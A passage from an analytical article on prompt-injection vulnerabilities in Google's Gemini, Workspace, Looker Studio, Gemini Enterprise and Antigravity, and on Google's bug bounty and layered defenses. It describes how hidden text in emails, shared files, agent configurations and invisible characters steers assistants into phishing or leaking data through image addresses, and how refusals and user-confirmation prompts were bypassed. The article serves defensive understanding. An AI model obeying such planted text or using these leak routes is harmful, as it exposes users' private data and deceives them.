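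Google also marked reports from the security company HiddenLayer as intended behavior. They concerned Gemini for Workspace, the assistant in Gmail, Docs and Google's other office products. *New Gemini for Workspace Vulnerability Enabling Phishing & Content Manipulation* (Martin and Yeung, 2024) describes an email with hidden text that made Gemini tell the recipient to change a compromised password at a fake address. In Google Slides, the researchers altered the summary of a presentation through its speaker notes, a problem Google said it already knew about. In Google Drive, they shared a document from one account and used it to control Gemini's answer in another.

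The leaks that Google repaired sent data to an outsider. In the Docs and Workspace reports, the planted text only changed what the user read, and it did no harm unless the user then called a number or visited a site. There is also a practical reason to treat them differently, since Google can stop a chat page from loading outside images but can't stop an assistant from using documents in its answers, which is the assistant's purpose.

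However, phishing is more serious than this distinction implies, because a warning from Google's own assistant is more convincing than the same warning in a stranger's email. The Drive test also showed that an outsider could get text into the prompt, the hardest part of an image leak, just by sharing a file. Google later built defenses against the kind of attack it had called intended behavior. It now tells Workspace users that Gemini may warn them about malicious content and may leave some or all of their content out of its answer.

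### The AI Vulnerability Reward Program

On 6 October 2025, Google moved AI reports from its abuse program to a dedicated AI Vulnerability Reward Program (AI VRP). In *How we're securing the AI frontier*, Kotsovinos and Flynn (2025) announced a single set of rules with reward tables for both abuse and security issues. They asked users to report harmful or false content through each product's feedback function, because it records details Google needs to diagnose the problem, such as the model version.

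A report qualifies if interaction with a language model or other generative AI system is an integral part of the flaw, according to Infosecurity Magazine's *Google Launches AI Bug Bounty with $30,000 Top Reward*. The categories include sensitive data exfiltration, unauthorized actions by the AI, phishing and model theft. An image leak now has its own category, and HiddenLayer's Gmail attack might too. One panel considers each report under both the abuse and security tables and pays the higher amount, so a researcher no longer loses money if Google classes a leak as abuse.

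Press accounts differ on whether prompt injection qualifies for a bounty. Infosecurity Magazine lists it as excluded, along with jailbreaks and alignment issues, while TechRadar's *Google launches AI bug bounties* lists it as covered. Both can be right if Google excludes injections that only produce odd or offensive text but pays for those that leak data.

The maximum reward depends on the product's tier. For sensitive data exfiltration, SecurityWeek reported a maximum of $15,000 for "flagship" and "standard" products and $10,000 for "other" products. The flagship tier includes Google Search, the Gemini app and the main Workspace applications. AI Studio is in a lower tier, apparently the standard one, along with Workspace's non-core applications. NotebookLM would qualify for the same maximum if Google counts it as one of those non-core applications. Colab's tier is less clear, so the maximum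 for a leak there could be either amount. Google can add bonuses for good or novel reports.

Google said it had paid more than $430,000 for AI-related issues before the new program began. According to its *VRP 2025 Year in Review*, Google awarded more than $400,000 for over 70 reports at one invitation-only hacking event in Tokyo in April 2025. If the first figure includes the second, researchers who reported AI flaws through the ordinary channel had received very little.

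### Google's layered defenses

Google does not rely on outside reports alone. Google's *Mitigating prompt injection attacks with a layered defense strategy* (2025), published on 13 June 2025, explains how the company protects the Gemini app and Gemini in Workspace. Google's case is that several imperfect defenses make an attack more expensive and easier to detect. If a user asks Gemini to summarize an email with planted text, the defenses work roughly as follows:

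1. Classifiers, which are separate machine learning models, check the email for malicious instructions and filter out what they detect.
2. Google adds reminders around the remaining text that tell Gemini to do the user's task and ignore other instructions.
3. Gemini itself has had training on examples of attacks, which Google calls model hardening, to make it more likely to ignore planted text.
4. Software checks the answer. It does not display images from outside addresses, and it removes links that Google's Safe Browsing service considers suspicious.
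5. If Gemini is about to do something risky, such as deleting a calendar event, the user may have to confirm it first.

Gemini also notifies the user when one of these defenses has stopped an attack.

The classifiers, the reminders and the training all depend on a model's judgment, so new wording may still get past them, as it got past the instruction in Colab's system prompt. Google DeepMind (2025) described an automated system that constantly attacks Gemini to find such weaknesses before outsiders do.

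The ban on outside images is different because it is deterministic, meaning the software applies the same rule whatever the model writes. Google said this ban made Gemini immune to EchoLeak, an image-based data leak that Aim Security had found in Microsoft 365 Copilot.

In *Google Workspace’s continuous approach to mitigating indirect prompt injections*, Gavish (2026) wrote that indirect prompt injection is not a problem one can solve and move on from. He classed user confirmation, URL sanitization and rules on how the assistant may combine its tools as deterministic defenses. Google's engineers can change these through a central configuration faster than they can retrain a model, so they can block a new attack this way first. They then generate variants of the attack, retrain the classifiers on some of them and test the result on others.

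Google measures each improvement by running simulated attacks against Gmail, Docs and other applications with the defense on and off. This is a sensible test. Gavish wrote that hardening had made attacks on Gemini succeed less often, but he gave no success rates, so an outsider can't tell how often they still work.

### Closing the ways out

Rehberger starts from the same problem but trusts the model less. He sees no deterministic fix for prompt injection, so in his NotebookLM post on Embrace The Red he advised against displaying images or clickable links that point to arbitrary domains.

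His later recommendations extend this to assistants that can take actions. He advises developers to avoid letting a model start sensitive operations automatically, including those that only retrieve data, because a request for a web page can leak data just as an image request can. Before any action, the application should show the user what it will do and which data it will use. He also wants developers to document the security guarantees their applications can provide.

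Neither Google nor Rehberger expects a cure for prompt injection, and both want applications to block outside images and ask users before risky actions. They disagree most clearly about links. Google removes links it considers suspicious, while Rehberger would remove every link to an arbitrary domain. Google's approach keeps useful links in an answer but may miss a link to a server that an attacker has just set up. Rehberger's approach doesn't depend on recognizing the attacker, but it would make an assistant less useful for research.

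Google and Willison also disagree about how much the other layers of defense are worth. On its security blog, Google had earlier recommended combining automated attacks, monitoring, heuristic defenses and standard security engineering, because it expected no single solution. Willison agreed that one seemed unlikely, but doubted that heuristic defenses, which catch many attacks without guaranteeing to catch all of them, would be enough to release such systems responsibly. Google's handling of image leaks supports his view, because Google did not leave the decision about outside images to a classifier.

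### Looker Studio and Gemini Enterprise

Google's ban on outside images covered the Gemini app and Workspace, but other Google products could still leak data through images. On 3 June 2025, ten days before Google published its account, the security company Tenable reported such a leak in Looker Studio, a tool for turning data into charts and reports. Tenable's *Google Cloud Platform (GCP) Cross-Tenant Data Sources Exfiltration through Conversational Analytics* describes an attacker who creates an AI agent that answers questions about data and gives it hidden instructions. Looker Studio didn't properly check which data sources an agent could use, so the attacker could attach one belonging to the victim. When the victim sent the agent any message, it retrieved the data with the victim's access and put it in an image's address.

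A classifier that checks emails and documents might not have stopped this attack, because the hidden instructions were in the agent's own configuration. A ban on outside images would have blocked this route wherever the instructions came from. But the flaw also included an ordinary missing check, which Google needed to fix with or without such a ban.

On 28 July, Google told Tenable that it had fixed the bug but still had to deal with a possible way around the fix. Google paid a reward on 12 August and said on 25 August, 83 days after the report, that the code for the repair was complete. Tenable delayed publication while Google worked, and confirms that Google has fixed the issue.

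Noma Security found a second leak in Gemini Enterprise, Google's assistant for searching a company's files, and in Vertex AI Search. According to SC Media's *Google addresses ‘GeminiJack’ exploit affecting Gemini Enterprise*, an attacker could plant instructions in an email, a calendar invitation or a shared document. When an employee made a relevant search, the assistant retrieved the planted text. It then searched the employee's emails, calendar and documents for whatever the attacker wanted, and sent the results out through an image.

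HiddenLayer had already shown that a shared document could control Gemini's answers in Drive, which Google called intended behavior. Noma's attack got its text to the assistant in a similar way, but it added an image that let the attacker steal company data instead of only misleading the user. Google fixed Noma's attack.

Noma reported the leak in June 2025, and Google resolved it by November. Noma wrote that the fix addressed the assistant's confusion between instructions and content when it retrieves documents. However, Noma's research lead, Sasi Levi, said Google had not disclosed the technical details and Noma did not know what had changed. It is therefore unclear whether Google blocked the route by which data leaked or made the planted text less effective.

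### Antigravity and the known-issues list

Google released Antigravity, a programming environment with a built-in AI agent, in November 2025. It was based on Windsurf, whose code Google had licensed in a deal worth about $2.4 billion. Rehberger had reported several flaws to Windsurf in May 2025, so he checked whether Antigravity still had them. Embrace the Red's *Antigravity Grounded! Security Vulnerabilities in Google's Latest IDE* confirms that it did, including a data leak through images that could expose a developer's passwords and access keys. He also found that data could leak through a tool for reading web pages, which the agent could use without asking permission.

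Willison (2025), in *Google Antigravity Exfiltrates Data*, quotes another researcher, who posts as P1njc70r and had reported the image leak, as saying that Google had flagged his report as intended behavior. Google's response does not fit the distinction between leaks and misleading answers, because the flaw sent private data to an outsider, as it had in Bard, NotebookLM and AI Studio.

Google then published a list of known issues in Antigravity, including data exfiltration through prompt injection, and said its team was working on fixes. Known issues do not earn rewards, which keeps Google from paying many people for the same flaw. The list also gave developers a warning that NotebookLM's users never received from Google in early 2024. But it does not protect anyone who hasn't read it, and researchers have less reason to look for further versions of a listed leak.

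Rehberger called the repairs relatively simple and suspected that the release had surprised Google's security team. In his tests, Gemini 3 and a model from Anthropic often refused plainly dangerous commands, but he found ways around the refusals in both. Gemini 3 also followed instructions written in characters invisible to the user, a weakness he had first reported when Google's chatbot was still called Bard. He found that the agent resisted attacks better when it planned and reasoned at length, so a stronger model may help, though he would not rely on one for security.

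Seven months later, researchers at 0DIN, a company that runs a reward program for AI flaws, demonstrated another image leak in Antigravity. In *Faking the Pipeline*, Odson and Morris (2026) showed that the leak worked even though the agent first asked the user for permission. The user approved the action because the agent described it as a harmless debugging step and showed neither the command nor the address that would receive the data.

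Google counts user confirmation among its deterministic defenses, but in this case the defense guaranteed only that a question would appear, and an agent under an attacker's control wrote that question. Google's example from the Gemini app is safer, because Gemini lists the calendar events it is about to delete. Rehberger had recommended in 2024 that applications show both the action and the data involved, and the 0DIN result supports that advice.

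Odson and Morris reported no fix. Google released a new version of Antigravity on 22 June 2026, five days after they published. According to a reply to Erick_Joseph in *Ah, did you change how the AI responds to security verifications?* on Google's developer forum, the agent now asks before it opens certain sensitive folders if the user has turned on a strict mode. This restricts what the agent can read but does not by itself stop the chat from loading an outside image.
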